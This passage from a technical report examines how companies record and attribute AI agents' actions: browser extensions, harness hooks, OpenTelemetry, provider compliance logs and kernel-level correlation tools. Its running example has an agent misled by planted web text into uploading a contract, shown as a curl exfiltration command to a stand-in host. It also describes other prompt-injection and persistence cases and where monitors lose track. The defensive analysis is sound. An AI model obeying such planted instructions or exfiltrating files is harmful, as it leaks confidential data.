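Strac sells both sensors, and its case is an illustration with no error rate. Strac labels the result "correlated" and rates this kind of attribution as low to medium confidence, which is more cautious than many vendors' claims. The case supports the modest conclusion that an extension can show what happened on a page, but identifying who did it usually also takes a record from the device or the agent software.

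A company can avoid some of this investigation by giving the agent a separate browser profile and, where the service allows it, its own account. As long as employees don't use that profile, any clicks in it were made by the agent.

### Browsers and pages without coverage

An extension records activity only in the browsers and profiles where it runs. If a company installs it in managed Chrome, it won't cover Firefox or a contractor's unmanaged browser. It also won't run in Chrome's incognito windows unless the user allows it, though a company can turn off incognito mode.

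Browsers built into desktop programs are a newer gap in what extensions can observe. Claude's desktop app has its own browser, and users can import cookies from their regular browser, the small files that keep them signed in to websites. Anthropic says this import is on by default on Team and Enterprise plans. The agent can then open webmail, signed in as the employee, in a browser without the company's extension.

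The same task can also move between browsers. If an employee asks for a browser without naming one and the preferred one is offline, Claude tells the employee and continues in the other. The company's extension might therefore record the email on Monday but record nothing when Claude does the same task on Tuesday. A company that depends on its extension could turn off the built-in browser, which Anthropic lets administrators do.

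OpenAI has made a similar change. It released a separate browser, Atlas, for the Mac in October 2025 and planned to retire it on 9 August 2026, according to BGR's *OpenAI Has Already Discontinued Its Controversial ChatGPT Atlas Browser*. Atlas was a poor source of records anyway. It sent no logs to OpenAI's compliance interface or to customers' security systems, according to the company's *ChatGPT Atlas for Enterprise*.

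OpenAI replaced Atlas with an updated Chrome extension, a browser in the ChatGPT desktop app and a cloud browser for agents. The Indian Express' *OpenAI to shut down ChatGPT Atlas browser* reports that the cloud browser runs on OpenAI's servers. A customer's extension can record what the agent does in an employee's Chrome, but not what it does on those servers.

Automated browsers on the company's own machines may lack the extension too. Developers often run them with a fresh profile or a separate copy of the browser, and an agent can start one for a single task. The company has to include the extension when setting up these browsers or find them with an endpoint sensor.

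An installed extension still misses some browser activity. According to Google, Chrome hides some sensitive requests from extensions because they are central to the browser's operation. Extensions also don't see requests that Chrome answers from its memory cache. An administrator can bar extensions from up to 100 sites or site patterns, and a broad rule could exclude the monitoring extension by mistake. Chrome also disables any extension older than the minimum version set by company policy, even one that the administrator forced it to install. Organisations should therefore check that each browser is still sending records.

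An extension also misses everything outside the browser, such as the command-line upload in step 5 or an email sent from a desktop mail program.

### The extension's own access

The access that makes an extension useful also makes it dangerous. If an extension can run on all sites, Chrome warns users that it can "Read and change all your data on the websites you visit", according to Google's *Declare permissions and warn users*. An extension with that permission can read confidential documents, private messages and passwords as people type them. It can also alter a page, so the company has to trust the extension's record of what the page originally showed.

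Employees cannot refuse an extension that an administrator force-installs. Google's *Automatically install apps and extensions* warns administrators that force-installing an extension gives it permission to access information on the device. After the first installation, Chrome normally takes updates from an address that the extension specifies, though an administrator can override it. An attacker who took over the supplier's account could expose web pages across the whole company with a single update.

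A company can reduce the danger by limiting the extension to sites where its agents work, such as webmail and the customer database. But a narrower list makes the extension less likely to record an upload to an unexpected site. An extension that covers every site, however, collects much more about employees than about agents, which may cause problems under employee monitoring law.

The extension provides an independent record only if the agent cannot change the browser's extensions or settings. Forced installation stops employees from removing the extension, and the company should apply the same restriction to any account the agent uses.

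### The six steps in the browser

The table applies when the agent runs on the laptop and uses the employee's own Chrome, and the extension covers all sites.

| Step | What the extension can record | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Exchange with the model | Nothing, because the harness is a separate program | Prompts and replies |
| 2. Reading the contracts | Nothing | The files opened |
| 3. Writing and running the script | Nothing | The script and the programs it started |
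| 4. Email to counsel | The account, recipient, subject and text, and the site's confirmation | Whether the agent or the employee clicked, and the request behind the email |
| 5. Web page and upload | The page and its planted text, if the agent opened it in Chrome | The upload from the command line |
| 6. Scheduled job | Nothing, unless the script opens a page in Chrome | The creation of the job and the next day's run |

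If the employee had used a chatbot's website instead, the extension could also record the conversation in step 1. For the document agent, the extension gives the most readable record of the email and may preserve the text that misled the agent, but it does not record the contract leaving the laptop.

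## The case for records from the agent software and its provider

A browser extension can record the email in step 4, but it can't show whether the agent or the employee sent it. The harness can show this because it carried out the tool call that clicked "Send". It also handles the employee's request, the model's replies and the arguments of every tool call as readable text, so a company can log them without decrypting traffic or attaching probes to a program.

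Records of approvals are even harder to get from other sources. When an employee clicks "Allow" to let a harness run a command, the click happens in the harness's own window. An endpoint sensor can record that the command ran, and a network tap can record the traffic it caused, but neither shows whether a person approved it.

The provider may have the only record of what an agent did in the cloud. If the task had run in a Cowork cloud session, the company would depend on Anthropic to learn which commands the agent ran in steps 3 and 5.

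A company can get such records from hooks in the harness, telemetry it exports, or an interface to the provider's logs.

### Hooks and Elastic's log of its own agents

Elastic's *13 million tool calls* describes how the company recorded what Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, did on its employees' computers. Elastic sells the software that stores and searches these logs, but it has also published the logging script, so readers can check how it works. When the agent wants to run a shell command, the following happens:

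1. Cursor pauses, starts the script and passes it a description of the event, including the command.
2. The script tells Cursor to go ahead.
3. The script adds a line to a log file on the computer.
4. Elastic's endpoint software sends the line to a central database.

Elastic didn't want to block anything, but it needed the events that make Cursor pause for a response. One contains the command before it runs, and another is the only record of file reads that Cursor provides. The script responds to Cursor before writing to the log, so that a disk error loses only a line in the log and doesn't leave the agent waiting. Similarly, if a hook fails without responding, Cursor goes ahead with the action unless the company has configured that hook to block on failure.

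If the document agent had hooks like Cursor's, the upload in step 5 might produce this entry, in a shortened version of Elastic's format with invented values:

```
{"timestamp":"2026-11-03T14:36:39Z", "user":"arossi",
 "host":"laptop-0417", "agent":"doc-agent", "session_id":"88",
 "hook_event_name":"beforeShellExecution", "tool_name":"Shell",
 "command":"curl -F \"file=@Supply agreement.pdf\" https://files.dropsite.example/upload"}
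```

An endpoint sensor would record the same command, but it would have to infer from process lineage that the agent requested it. The hook records the agent's request directly and adds the session.

In the two months after the rollout in May, Elastic logged more than 13 million events from over 1,100 machines and nearly 900 users. File reads outnumbered shell commands by about four to one, which surprised its staff. Elastic also found more than 300 MCP servers in the log, and 86% of them had only one or two users. Until then, it knew only about the servers that employees remembered to mention. The hooks would therefore help any company fill in its register.

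Elastic chose not to log prompts, replies or file contents so that it could assure developers that nobody was reading their conversations. As a result, its log would contain the upload in step 5 but not the planted text that caused it.

Elastic also found that hooks can be installed but not working. Cursor reads its hook settings only when it starts, so the deployment tool reported success on machines that were sending nothing. Cursor also silently skips any script whose file path contains a space. A company that uses hooks should check that events arrive from every machine.

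### OpenTelemetry

OpenTelemetry is an open standard for sending records of a program's activity to monitoring systems. A program can describe each operation as a "span", which has a start, an end and a set of named fields. The project's conventions for generative AI specify what those fields should be called. The main ones for a call to an agent, from OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans*, are:

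| Field | What it holds | Requirement |
|---|---|---|
| `gen_ai.operation.name` | The kind of operation, such as invoking an agent | Required |
| `gen_ai.provider.name` | The model's provider | Required |
| `gen_ai.agent.id` | The agent's identifier | Required if applicable |
| `gen_ai.conversation.id` | The session | Required when available |
| `gen_ai.request.model` | The model requested | Required when available |
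| `gen_ai.usage.input_tokens` | The amount of text sent to the model | Recommended |
| `gen_ai.input.messages` | The conversation sent to the model | Opt-in |
| `gen_ai.system_instructions` | The standing instructions | Opt-in |

OpenTelemetry also defines fields for a tool call's identifier and its arguments. If the agent used a mail tool, the company would find the recipient in step 4 among the arguments.

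Because recording the conversation is opt-in, a harness can follow the conventions fully without exporting any prompt text. Many providers accept requests in OpenAI's format, and OpenTelemetry warns that the provider field is based on the information available to the recording software and may differ from the actual provider. A company that wants to know who received its contracts should compare the field with the server address.

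The conventions are unfinished. Greptime (2026), a database vendor, reported in May that the core concepts had settled but the conventions were still in "Development" status, with no public timetable for a stable version. The project has since moved them to a separate repository (OpenTelemetry, *Moved*). Wang's *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (2026) dates the move to June and says the new repository had no official release as of 21 August. Companies can use the conventions now but should expect to rewrite some searches when field names change.

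Two products that support OpenTelemetry can still send quite different records. Cowork, for example, has its own events, including `user_prompt`, `tool_result` and `tool_decision`. According to Anthropic, it attaches the same `prompt.id` to everything that follows from one prompt, so an investigator can collect all the tool calls that resulted from the request about the contracts.

The `tool_decision` event records approvals, which the other routes do not capture. Anthropic's *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* says the export shows whether the user approved an action, the user rejected it, or Cowork started it under existing permissions. In Cowork's automatic mode, a classifier (software that judges whether a call is acceptable) can make the decision, and the event then includes its verdict, so an investigator can tell whether an employee or the software approved the action.

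### How Cowork's records developed

Anthropic gives business customers several kinds of record. Its audit logs list events such as a user creating a chat, but Anthropic says exported logs contain only identifiers, not chat titles or content. Data exports contain a customer's content in bulk. The Compliance API lets a customer's own software retrieve both events and conversations.

Anthropic released Cowork as a research preview on 12 January 2026, according to its *Release notes* (2026). In late March, Anthropic's *Use Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* (2026) still warned that audit logs, the Compliance API and data exports did not capture Cowork activity. Conversation history stayed on users' computers, where administrators could not export it. Anthropic told organisations that needed audit trails: "do not enable Cowork for regulated workloads". It offered OpenTelemetry for tracking usage,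 costs and tool activity, but said this did not replace audit logging.

*Claude Cowork*, Syracuse University's assessment for staff, called the missing records the most critical concern and concluded that the university would have no central view of what Cowork did or which files it accessed. By late March this was slightly overstated, because OpenTelemetry could report some tool activity. But the university was right that it could not have retrieved a conversation after an incident.

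Cowork became generally available on 9 April. On the same day, Anthropic's *Making Claude Cowork ready for enterprise* announced a fuller OpenTelemetry export, with events for tool calls, files and approvals. The export also included a shared account identifier so that customers could match these events with Compliance API records, but those records did not include Cowork sessions until nearly four months later.

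According to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026), the Compliance API began on 3 August to return Cowork sessions that users had started on the web or a phone and that ran in Anthropic's cloud. On 11 August it added Cowork and Claude Code sessions on users' own machines. Both additions were in beta and available only to Enterprise customers. Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* listed three exclusions from the beta: Claude Code on the web, Claude Code through Anthropic's developer platform, and sessions run on Amazon's, Google's or Microsoft's AI services.

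The beta ended for Cowork and Claude Code on 26 August, so warnings from the spring that Anthropic keeps no audit record of Cowork are out of date for Enterprise customers. Customers on the cheaper Team plan can't retrieve the transcripts and still depend on OpenTelemetry.

### What the Compliance API holds now

For sessions on a user's machine, Anthropic records the conversation on its own servers as each request reaches the model, and the organisation doesn't have to install anything. According to Anthropic's *Retrieve session transcripts*, this record shows what Claude was asked and returned, "not what occurred on the device".

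Anthropic records these local sessions only while the customer has the Compliance API on and the user is signed in with an Enterprise account. The same setting controls the activity feed, a log of account events. Anthropic warns customers that activity missed while the API is off can't be recovered later. If the company in the example had turned the API on a week after the task, it would have no transcript of a session that ran on the laptop.

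Some sessions are still missing even when the interface is on:

- Claude Code sessions that use a developer's API key, or that run through Amazon Bedrock, Google Cloud or Microsoft Foundry
- Claude Code sessions in the cloud, including scheduled tasks
- local sessions under a zero data retention arrangement
- local sessions from products other than Cowork and Claude Code, if the customer has turned on Anthropic's configuration for American health data

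The transcripts also omit the model's reasoning and the standing instructions, and they replace images and PDFs with short placeholders. If the agent in the example had worked from screenshots of webmail, the transcript could contain its clicks and typing but not the page it was acting on.

The planted text in step 5 could be missing too. Anthropic replaces web search results with a placeholder, and by default it cuts each text result from a tool after 10,000 bytes. An investigator can ask for up to about a megabyte per result, and should before concluding that a web page contained nothing suspicious.

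Neither the transcript nor the OpenTelemetry export has everything about a Cowork session:

| Information | Compliance API transcript | OpenTelemetry export |
|---|---|---|
| Prompts and replies | Yes | Only if the company turns on content |
| Arguments of tool calls | Yes, up to the size limit | Shortened, and only if the company turns on content |
| Text that tools returned | Yes, up to the size limit | No, only details such as size and success |
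| Who or what approved a call | No separate entry | Yes |
| Who stores the record | Anthropic | The customer |
| How long it lasts | Six years by default for local sessions | As long as the customer chooses |

To investigate step 5, the company would need the transcript to find the planted text and the export to check whether the employee approved the upload.

Enterprise customers can also use inference hooks, which left beta on 20 October. Before Claude answers a prompt in chat, Cowork or Claude Code, Anthropic sends the prompt to a server that the customer controls, and the server allows or refuses it. Anthropic records every refusal in the activity feed. The customer's server could also keep a copy of the prompts.

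### Microsoft Agent 365

Microsoft's equivalent covers agents from more than one maker. Agent 365 is its system for managing the agents in an organisation's Microsoft account, and it passes their records to Microsoft's security software. Scalzi, who writes for the security firm Compass Security, lists the agents that this software can monitor:

- agents that employees build in Copilot Studio, which requires little programming
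- agents that developers build in Microsoft Foundry
- agents that users create inside Microsoft 365 Copilot
- other companies' agents, if their developers used Microsoft's Agent 365 toolkit
- local agents, which Defender observes on the device, partly through their hooks

The list excludes Microsoft 365 Copilot and Security Copilot because Microsoft runs both as its own assistants. Purview audits them instead, and a company can copy those records into Sentinel, Microsoft's system for collecting security logs. An investigator who searches only the Agent 365 records would find an employee's custom agent but not that employee's questions to Copilot.

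Each managed agent gets its own identity in the company's directory, with named owners and a log of its sign-ins. This provides much of what a register needs and helps attribute actions to the agent when it uses its own identity. It doesn't help in step 4, where the agent works in the employee's webmail session.

The company has to pay for the Agent 365 licence, or a larger bundle that includes it, and then turn on several settings. One connects Microsoft 365's logs and another covers Copilot Studio. A third lets the security team see extracts from prompts. Without it, the team might get an alert about an agent but not the prompt text that led to the alert. Scalzi notes that some of the logs in Sentinel also need separate configuration.

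### One format for several harnesses

A company whose employees use Claude Code, Codex and Cursor gets records in several formats. To find every agent that uploaded a file, its security team would have to write a separate search for each format and revise it when the supplier changed its software.

Help Net Security's *Agent Beacon* describes an attempt to fix this. Beacon, a free program from Asymptote Labs, configures Claude Code and Codex to send OpenTelemetry data to a collector on the same machine. For Cursor, it installs hooks and, unlike Elastic's script, also collects prompts. It converts all the data into a single event format. It can also include data from Cowork if an administrator has turned on Cowork's export.

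Beacon records everything it can by default, with options to leave out prompts, command output and other content. It can't add information that a harness doesn't send, so two agents' records may have the same fields but contain very different amounts of information. It also doesn't monitor processes, shell history or most browser activity.

Asymptote's chief executive, Justin D'Souza, presents Beacon as a foundation for rules that detect suspicious behaviour by any agent. He told Help Net Security that standardising such rules remains an open problem because the industry has no common format for agent activity. His company would benefit if its own format became the common one, but Elastic has also had trouble with inconsistent formats. It had to reorganise its own log because different types of hook event stored the same detail in different places.

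### Where these records have gaps

The most avoidable gap comes from default settings. Cowork exports nothing through OpenTelemetry until an administrator enters a destination address, and current versions then send only metadata by default. If the agent had sent the email through an MCP mail tool, the company would learn that a tool had run successfully and how long it took, but not the recipient or even the names of the MCP server and tool, which count as content.

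To include content, the company must change a setting on each employee's device. Some older versions of the desktop app send content without this change, so two colleagues on different versions can leave different records of the same task. The setting has no effect on Cowork sessions started on the web or a phone, which Anthropic says send only metadata. If an employee of a Team customer starts a task on a phone, the company gets no prompt text from OpenTelemetry and can't retrieve a transcript.

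Unapproved agents are a harder problem, because the company can configure hooks and exports only for software it manages. Even an approved program can go unrecorded if an employee uses it with a personal account. Elastic, for example, distributes some of its hooks through its company Cursor account, so they don't reach anyone who signs in with a personal one. Elastic recommends comparing the hook records with a separate inventory of the agents on each device, which would reveal agents that are installed but produce no hook records.

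The harness also misses the child processes that the script starts in step 3. Anthropic seems to accept that its own records are not enough here. For Cowork sessions on a user's computer, Anthropic now lets administrators run their own endpoint sensor inside the virtual machine where Cowork executes code. The feature is in beta and doesn't cover cloud sessions.

Finally, the company relies on the agent software to report on itself. A hook runs only if the harness calls it, and Elastic acknowledges that a developer with administrator rights can remove the hooks or edit the script. An agent with the same rights probably could too. A transcript on the provider's servers is harder to alter from the laptop, but its record of what a tool did still comes from the harness.

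### The six steps in the agent's own records

The table applies when the document agent runs on the laptop, supports hooks or telemetry, and has content recording turned on.

| Step | What the harness can record | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Exchange with the model | Prompts, replies, the model's name and the amount of text | Anything beyond a size limit |
| 2. Reading the contracts | The tool calls that opened files, with their paths | Files that a script or shell command opened by itself |
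| 3. Writing and running the script | The script, the command that ran it and what it printed | The programs it started and the files they opened |
| 4. Email to counsel | The request, the agent's clicks and typing, and any approval | The mail service's own record of the message |
| 5. Web page and upload | The planted text, the upload command and the reported result | Independent evidence of what left the laptop |
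| 6. Scheduled job | The command that created the job | The next day's run |

If the employee had used Cowork in the cloud and Cowork's own scheduler, the Compliance API would also have a transcript of the next day's run, but an investigator could easily overlook it. Anthropic stores each scheduled run as a separate session, without the task's name, that belongs to an agent instead of a user. A search for all of A. Rossi's cloud sessions would miss the run because searches by user leave out sessions that belong to agents.

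## How records from different places are joined

None of the four routes gives a full account of the document agent's task. Some companies that sell monitoring argue that one monitor in the right place is enough, while others argue that an organisation has to collect records in several places and match them.

### One monitor or several

In *From Packets to Agent Chains*, Mandal and Garg argue for a single monitor. Their company, Aurva, sells software that uses eBPF to record the processes and network traffic on a customer's servers, and they claim it leaves "no gaps in coverage". In their example, a customer-support agent queries a customer database, sends the results to a model, opens a support ticket and posts a message to colleagues. The agent then compresses the whole conversation, including the customer data, and uploads it to a personal site. Every login and permission check succeeds.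 A reviewer who looked at each step separately might approve them all, but the sequence shows customer data leaving the company.

This is a good argument for linking an agent's steps together, but a weaker one for using a single monitor. Aurva's software keeps only one in a hundred of the model calls it classifies as routine, so it has to predict at the time which calls will matter later. It also can't run on a model provider's servers. Collecting everything in one place makes events easier to link, but the software still has to match them by process lineage, connection and time.

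Sysdig sells monitoring for both the harness and the kernel, and argues that security teams need both. Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents* reports the company's finding that the kernel runs about seven processes for every action an agent logs. This is an early figure from a product launch, and Sysdig doesn't say how many agents it observed or what kinds of task they performed. The figure suggests that security teams can't match the two records by pairing each log entry with one process. It doesn't mean that most of the processes did anything suspicious, because one ordinary shell command can start several programs.

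The open-source project Falco, on which Sysdig's product builds, also offers both hook-based checks and kernel monitoring. Its new tool, Prempti, checks tool calls through a hook, but a hook can't follow what a program does after it starts. *Introducing Prempti* (2026), from CNCF, the foundation that hosts Falco, recommends Falco's kernel monitoring for that.

Investigators have more reason to combine records when they have to explain an incident as well as detect it, because the kernel events show what happened on the machine but the reason is usually in the conversation.

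### The request and the system events

Steps 3 and 5 look alike on the laptop because in both, the harness starts a shell, which starts programs that read contracts. Step 3 is legitimate because the employee asked for a summary and the script extracts the text for it, but nobody asked for the upload in step 5.

Zheng and colleagues call the distance between an agent's stated intention and the resulting system events a "semantic gap". A monitor inside the application might record only that the tool call "execute script" succeeded, even if the script was harmful. A monitor in the kernel might record a shell writing to a file, which would look the same whether the agent was analysing data or planting malicious code. Bao and colleagues make the same point about the file where Linux keeps scheduled jobs. An agent that adds a line to it may be doing what the user wanted or something the user would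 never have allowed, and the only way to tell is to check the user's request.

Wong and Chen (2026), in *ExecWeave*, add that a command in the harness's log doesn't prove that the program ran, and a connection in the kernel's log doesn't identify the tool call that asked for it. Joining the two records is therefore an inference, which can be wrong even when both records are right.

### AgentSight: lineage, time and arguments

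Zheng and colleagues built AgentSight in 2025 to make these links automatically on Linux. It uses probes on the TLS library to copy the harness's prompts and the model's replies, and it also collects kernel events, such as programs starting, files opening and connections to other machines. A filter in the kernel discards events from any process that doesn't descend from the agent.

AgentSight then looks for three signs that a model's reply led to a system event:

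- **Lineage:** the process descends from the harness.
- **Time:** the event follows the reply within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Arguments:** a file name, web address or command in the reply also appears in the system call.

All three could apply to the upload in step 5. The model's reply contains the `curl` command and the address files.dropsite.example, the harness starts a shell almost at once, and the shell starts `curl` with the same arguments. But if the harness waits for the employee to approve the command, the window will probably close before the shell starts, and the match will depend on lineage and arguments.

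Finally, AgentSight sends the linked events to a second language model, which is instructed to act as a security analyst and returns a written assessment with a confidence score. This model can flag an action that doesn't fit the user's request even if no rule covers that action. Its input may also include the same planted text that misled the agent, and Zheng and colleagues don't test whether that text could mislead the second model too.

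The AgentSight paper measures the slowdown by running Claude Code on three tasks, three times each with AgentSight and three times without. Exploring a code repository took 3.4% longer with AgentSight, writing code 4.9% longer and compiling a repository 0.4% longer. The paper's claim of less than 3% overhead holds for the average (2.9%) but not for exploring a repository or writing code. Three runs are too few to establish these percentages precisely, because an agent's running time varies anyway and the code-writing difference was only about one second.

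The AgentSight paper reports one test of attack detection, in which an agent was asked to download and build a software project whose README file sent it to a web page with hidden instructions. The agent followed them and sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server, as if this were part of the build. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37. A second model classified these as an attack with high confidence, because the actions didn't fit the agent's stated goal.

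The case shows that the method can work, but gives almost no evidence of how often it does. A system that caught only one attack in twenty could still pass a single test. Zheng and colleagues also report no tests on harmless tasks, so the method's false-alarm rate is unknown. Reducing 521 events to 37 makes the trace far easier to read, but they don't report checking whether each merged event was attached to the right reply.

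The other two cases involve faulty agents, not attacks. In one, an agent kept repeating a web search with the same wrong arguments. In the other, six coding agents produced 3,153 events after merging, and some of the agents blocked each other by locking the same files. This second problem would have been hard to find from the logs of each agent's own application alone.

### AgentLoupe: labels that pass through files

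Bao and colleagues presented AgentLoupe in autumn 2026 to address a case that AgentSight can't trace. An attacker gets an agent to install an hourly job that gives an outside machine control of the computer, and the operating system's scheduler starts the job an hour later.

The scheduler doesn't descend from the agent, so AgentSight's filter discards the event. Even without the filter, the event couldn't be linked to the agent by time, because an hour is far longer than half a second. Matching the arguments might show that the job's file has the same name as one the agent wrote, but that doesn't prove it is the same file.

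AgentLoupe doesn't try to reconstruct the link afterwards. It attaches a label to the agent's activity at the start and passes it on:

1. When the harness sends a new prompt, AgentLoupe gives the sending process a new number, which is the label.
2. Any process that this process starts inherits the label.
3. When a labelled process writes a file, AgentLoupe stores the label with the file's identity in the kernel.
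4. Any process that later opens or runs the file takes on the label, even if the agent has long since stopped.
5. Labels also pass through sockets, the channels that programs use to exchange data. A labelled process marks the socket when it connects or sends, and a process that receives data through the socket takes on the label.

Every recorded event carries its label, so an investigator can collect everything that followed from one prompt with a single search.

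Without limits, the labels would spread until they covered most of the machine. AgentLoupe therefore starts a new label for each independent prompt and keeps a reference to the old label if the two are connected. Users can also exclude sources of noise and set labels to expire.

Bao and colleagues measured both tools on the same machine, with five runs of each task. The table also shows results from Zheng and colleagues, who used a different machine and different projects.

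| Task | AgentSight, original test | AgentSight, repeated by Bao and colleagues | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a repository | 3.4% | 4.5% | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 4.9% | 2.5% | 8.0% |
| Compiling | 0.4% | 1.7% | 7.7% |

AgentLoupe adds more overhead on two of the tasks, mainly because it passes labels on. With label passing switched off, compiling was 0.1% faster than with no monitoring. Monitoring can't speed up a computer, so differences of that size are noise.

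In the first of two case studies, Bao and colleagues carried out the scheduled-job attack. AgentLoupe produced 165 log entries covering five exchanges with the model, and its labels linked the later network connection to the user's original request. A second model rated the threat at level 5, with a confidence of 0.95.

The other case involved AGENTS.md, a file of standing instructions that coding agents read. One session added an instruction to it that made ordinary requests trigger a command, and a separate session later read the file and ran the command. AgentLoupe linked the two sessions through the label on the file, in a trace of 126 log entries. Process lineage could not have linked them, because neither session started the other.

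Bao and colleagues argue from AgentSight's design that it would fail in both cases, but leave a direct comparison on such cases to future work. Their argument is convincing for the scheduled job, because AgentSight discards the relevant events before it tries to match them. However, they acknowledge they haven't measured how often AgentLoupe's own labels create false links or miss real ones.

### The scheduled job in step 6

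Suppose the employee's laptop runs Linux, which both tools require. AgentSight could link the creation of the scheduled job to the reply containing the request for it, but would have no record of the next day's run. AgentLoupe would have stored a label with the script when the agent wrote it, so the next day's run would carry a number that can be traced back to the employee's request about the contracts.

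The label may not last that long, though. Cui and colleagues built a similar tool, Agent-Warden, which labels processes and files but doesn't read prompts. They ran a prepared task with a known chain of events 30 times on each of four set-ups, and the tool reconstructed the whole chain every time, with an overhead of 0.2% to 3.5%. But they warn that the file labels disappear when the computer restarts and can disappear when it runs short of memory. AgentLoupe also keeps its labels in memory, and Bao and colleagues don't describe saving them to disk, so the link is probably lost if the employee shuts the laptop down overnight.

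These methods can also create false links. Under AgentLoupe's rules, the scheduler could take on the label when it opens the agent's job file and then pass it to unrelated jobs, such as a nightly backup. Expiry times and exclusions might prevent this, but if the label expired too soon, AgentLoupe would miss the run in step 6. Agent-Warden allows some false links by design. When a process that the agent started ends, the tool marks that process's parent as influenced, even if the parent never used the result.

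A company without either tool can still search its ordinary endpoint records for the script's path. One entry should show the agent's process writing the file, and another should show the scheduler running it the next day. This search is slower and works only if the file keeps its name, but the records survive a restart.

### When an agent uses a person's account

Labels in the kernel don't leave the machine, so they don't reach the mail service, which logs the email in step 4 as A. Rossi's.

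*Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) describes three situations in which an organisation can identify the agent at fault but not the person accountable for it. The agent may work through an account that several people share or nobody owns. It may serve several people without a record of whose task it was doing. Or the organisation's directory may not link the agent's identity to an accountable person. Claude Tag, a version of Claude that people can call on in a Slack channel, could easily cause the second problem. It works under the organisation's shared identity, and Anthropic warns customers not to rely on the user fields in its telemetry to find out who asked.

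The usual advice is to give each agent its own identity. In Entra, Microsoft's directory of accounts, a company can create an agent identity from a template called a blueprint. Some agents also get their own user account. According to Microsoft, the `agentType` field in the audit log distinguishes agents from people and ordinary applications, and the `blueprintId` field identifies the template. The sign-in log has a filter for agents. Scalzi notes that an agent's identity links its records in Defender, Entra and the Microsoft 365 admin centre.

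Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about how well this works. Another Microsoft page says audit logs don't distinguish agents from other identities by default, and tells administrators to look up each identity separately or follow a correlation identifier from the sign-in log. The logs of requests to Microsoft Graph, the interface through which programs reach Microsoft 365 data, list an agent as an application or a user, so an investigator has to join them with the sign-in log to find out which entries came from agents.

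The agent in step 4 also couldn't open webmail under its own identity if the site relied on Entra's sign-in pages, because agent identities can't use those pages. Microsoft recommends connecting agents to services through programming interfaces, which is another reason to give the document agent a mail tool.

Delegated credentials let a service record both the person and the agent. A program normally proves its right to use a service with a token, a small signed file. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* recommends tokens with separate entries for the person who gave authority and the agent that is using it. With invented values and most fields left out, a token for the email might contain:

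```
{"sub":"arossi", "aud":"mail.company.example",
 "act":{"sub":"doc-agent-12"}}
```

Here `sub` is the person, `aud` is the service and `act` is the agent acting for the person. The mail service could then log both the person and the agent, if its developers built it to read and store the `act` entry. The token still wouldn't show why the agent acted, and it would be the same if planted text on a web page had caused the email.

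A correlation identifier can connect the action to a particular request. Claude Code and Cowork both record a `prompt.id`, and Claude Code also records a `tool_use_id` for each tool call. When tracing is on, Claude Code gives each shell command a label called `TRACEPARENT` and sends a similar label with its requests to MCP servers over the web. According to Anthropic, when an agent hands work to a subagent, the subagent's tool calls appear beneath the parent's call in the same trace.

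Tracing is still in beta and off by default. Only programs written to use the label can do so, and `curl` isn't one of them. If a company sends Claude Code's model requests through its own gateway, Claude Code also stops passing the label on unless an administrator changes another setting.

The scheduled job also raises a question of authority, because it runs under A. Rossi's account a day after the session that created it. Bengio and colleagues say that organisations need clear rules for agents that keep running after the user's session ends, including whether the agents' credentials expire or need fresh approval.

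### A worked join for step 5

The upload in step 5 left records in the harness, on the device and on the network. The table shows them side by side. It reuses the invented values from earlier and adds the numbers that identify the tool call, the process and the local port.

| Field | Harness hook | Endpoint sensor | Network tap |
|---|---|---|---|
| Time (UTC) | 14:36:39 | 14:36:40 | 14:36:41 |
| Device | laptop-0417 | laptop-0417, address 10.20.4.76 | 10.20.4.76 |
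| User | arossi | A. Rossi | Not recorded |
| Session and tool call | Session 88, call 52 | Not recorded | Not recorded |
| Command | `curl`, with the file and web address | The same | Not recorded |
| Process | doc-agent | `curl` (process 7741), started by bash, started by doc-agent | Not recorded |
| Connection | Only the site's name, in the command | TCP, port 51844 to 203.0.113.50, port 443 | The same |
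| Data sent | Not recorded | Not recorded | 1,843,200 bytes |

An investigator who starts from the unusual upload on the network could join the records like this:

1. Take the two addresses, the two ports and the protocol from the flow record, and find the connection with the same values in the endpoint records. This leads to process 7741, `curl`.
2. Follow the process lineage upwards from `curl` to bash and then to doc-agent.
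3. Search the harness's log for a tool call on laptop-0417 with the same command, shortly before the process started. This leads to call 52 in session 88.
4. Read session 88 to find the employee's request and the web page with the planted instruction.

The harness log and the network tap log share no field that matches exactly, so the endpoint record has to connect them. Timestamps help narrow the search, but clocks on different machines can differ by more than a second, so the order of entries is weak evidence of the order of events.

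Step 1 is tedious because each product writes addresses and ports in its own way. Community ID, an open standard, turns these values into one short string that is the same in every product that supports it. Kreibich (2019), in *An update on Community ID*, explains that comparing this string replaces matching on several fields, a method that can go wrong in unusual cases. Security Onion, a free monitoring system, turns Community ID on for both of its network monitors, Zeek and Suricata (*Community ID*). Tenzir, which sells software for processing such data, recommends it for finding the process and user behind a connection (*Unifying network and endpoint data with Community IDs*).

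The string identifies a set of addresses and ports, which a computer can reuse, so the investigator still has to compare the records' times. The strings also won't match if a proxy or a shared internet connection changes the laptop's address before the traffic reaches the tap.

Step 3 depends on the harness's settings. Claude Code, for example, includes the full command in its telemetry only if the company turns on detailed logging. Otherwise the entry has the tool's name, the time and the duration, and the investigator has to choose among the shell commands the agent ran around that time.

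### When a record is missing or two records fit

Without one of the three records, the investigator can still establish part of what happened.

| Missing record | What the other two establish | What the company loses |
|---|---|---|
| Harness | A shell that doc-agent started ran `curl`, and 1.8 megabytes left the laptop | The session, the employee's request and the planted instruction |
| Endpoint sensor | The agent asked for an upload, and the laptop sent 1.8 megabytes at about that time | Proof that the agent's command made the connection |
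| Network tap | The agent asked for the upload, and `curl` ran and connected | An independent measure of how much data left |

If the endpoint record is missing, the DNS log can partly replace it by linking the site named in the agent's command to the address in the flow record. That makes the match likely, but another program on the laptop could have contacted the same site.

If the agent had run in its provider's cloud, the company would have only the provider's record of the upload and could not check it against records of its own.

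Having too many candidates is also a problem. Suppose doc-agent had two subagents inside the same harness process, and both ran `curl` within a second of each other. Both uploads would have the same lineage and nearly the same time. If the harness recorded only that each subagent had used the shell, an investigator couldn't tell which one had sent the contract.

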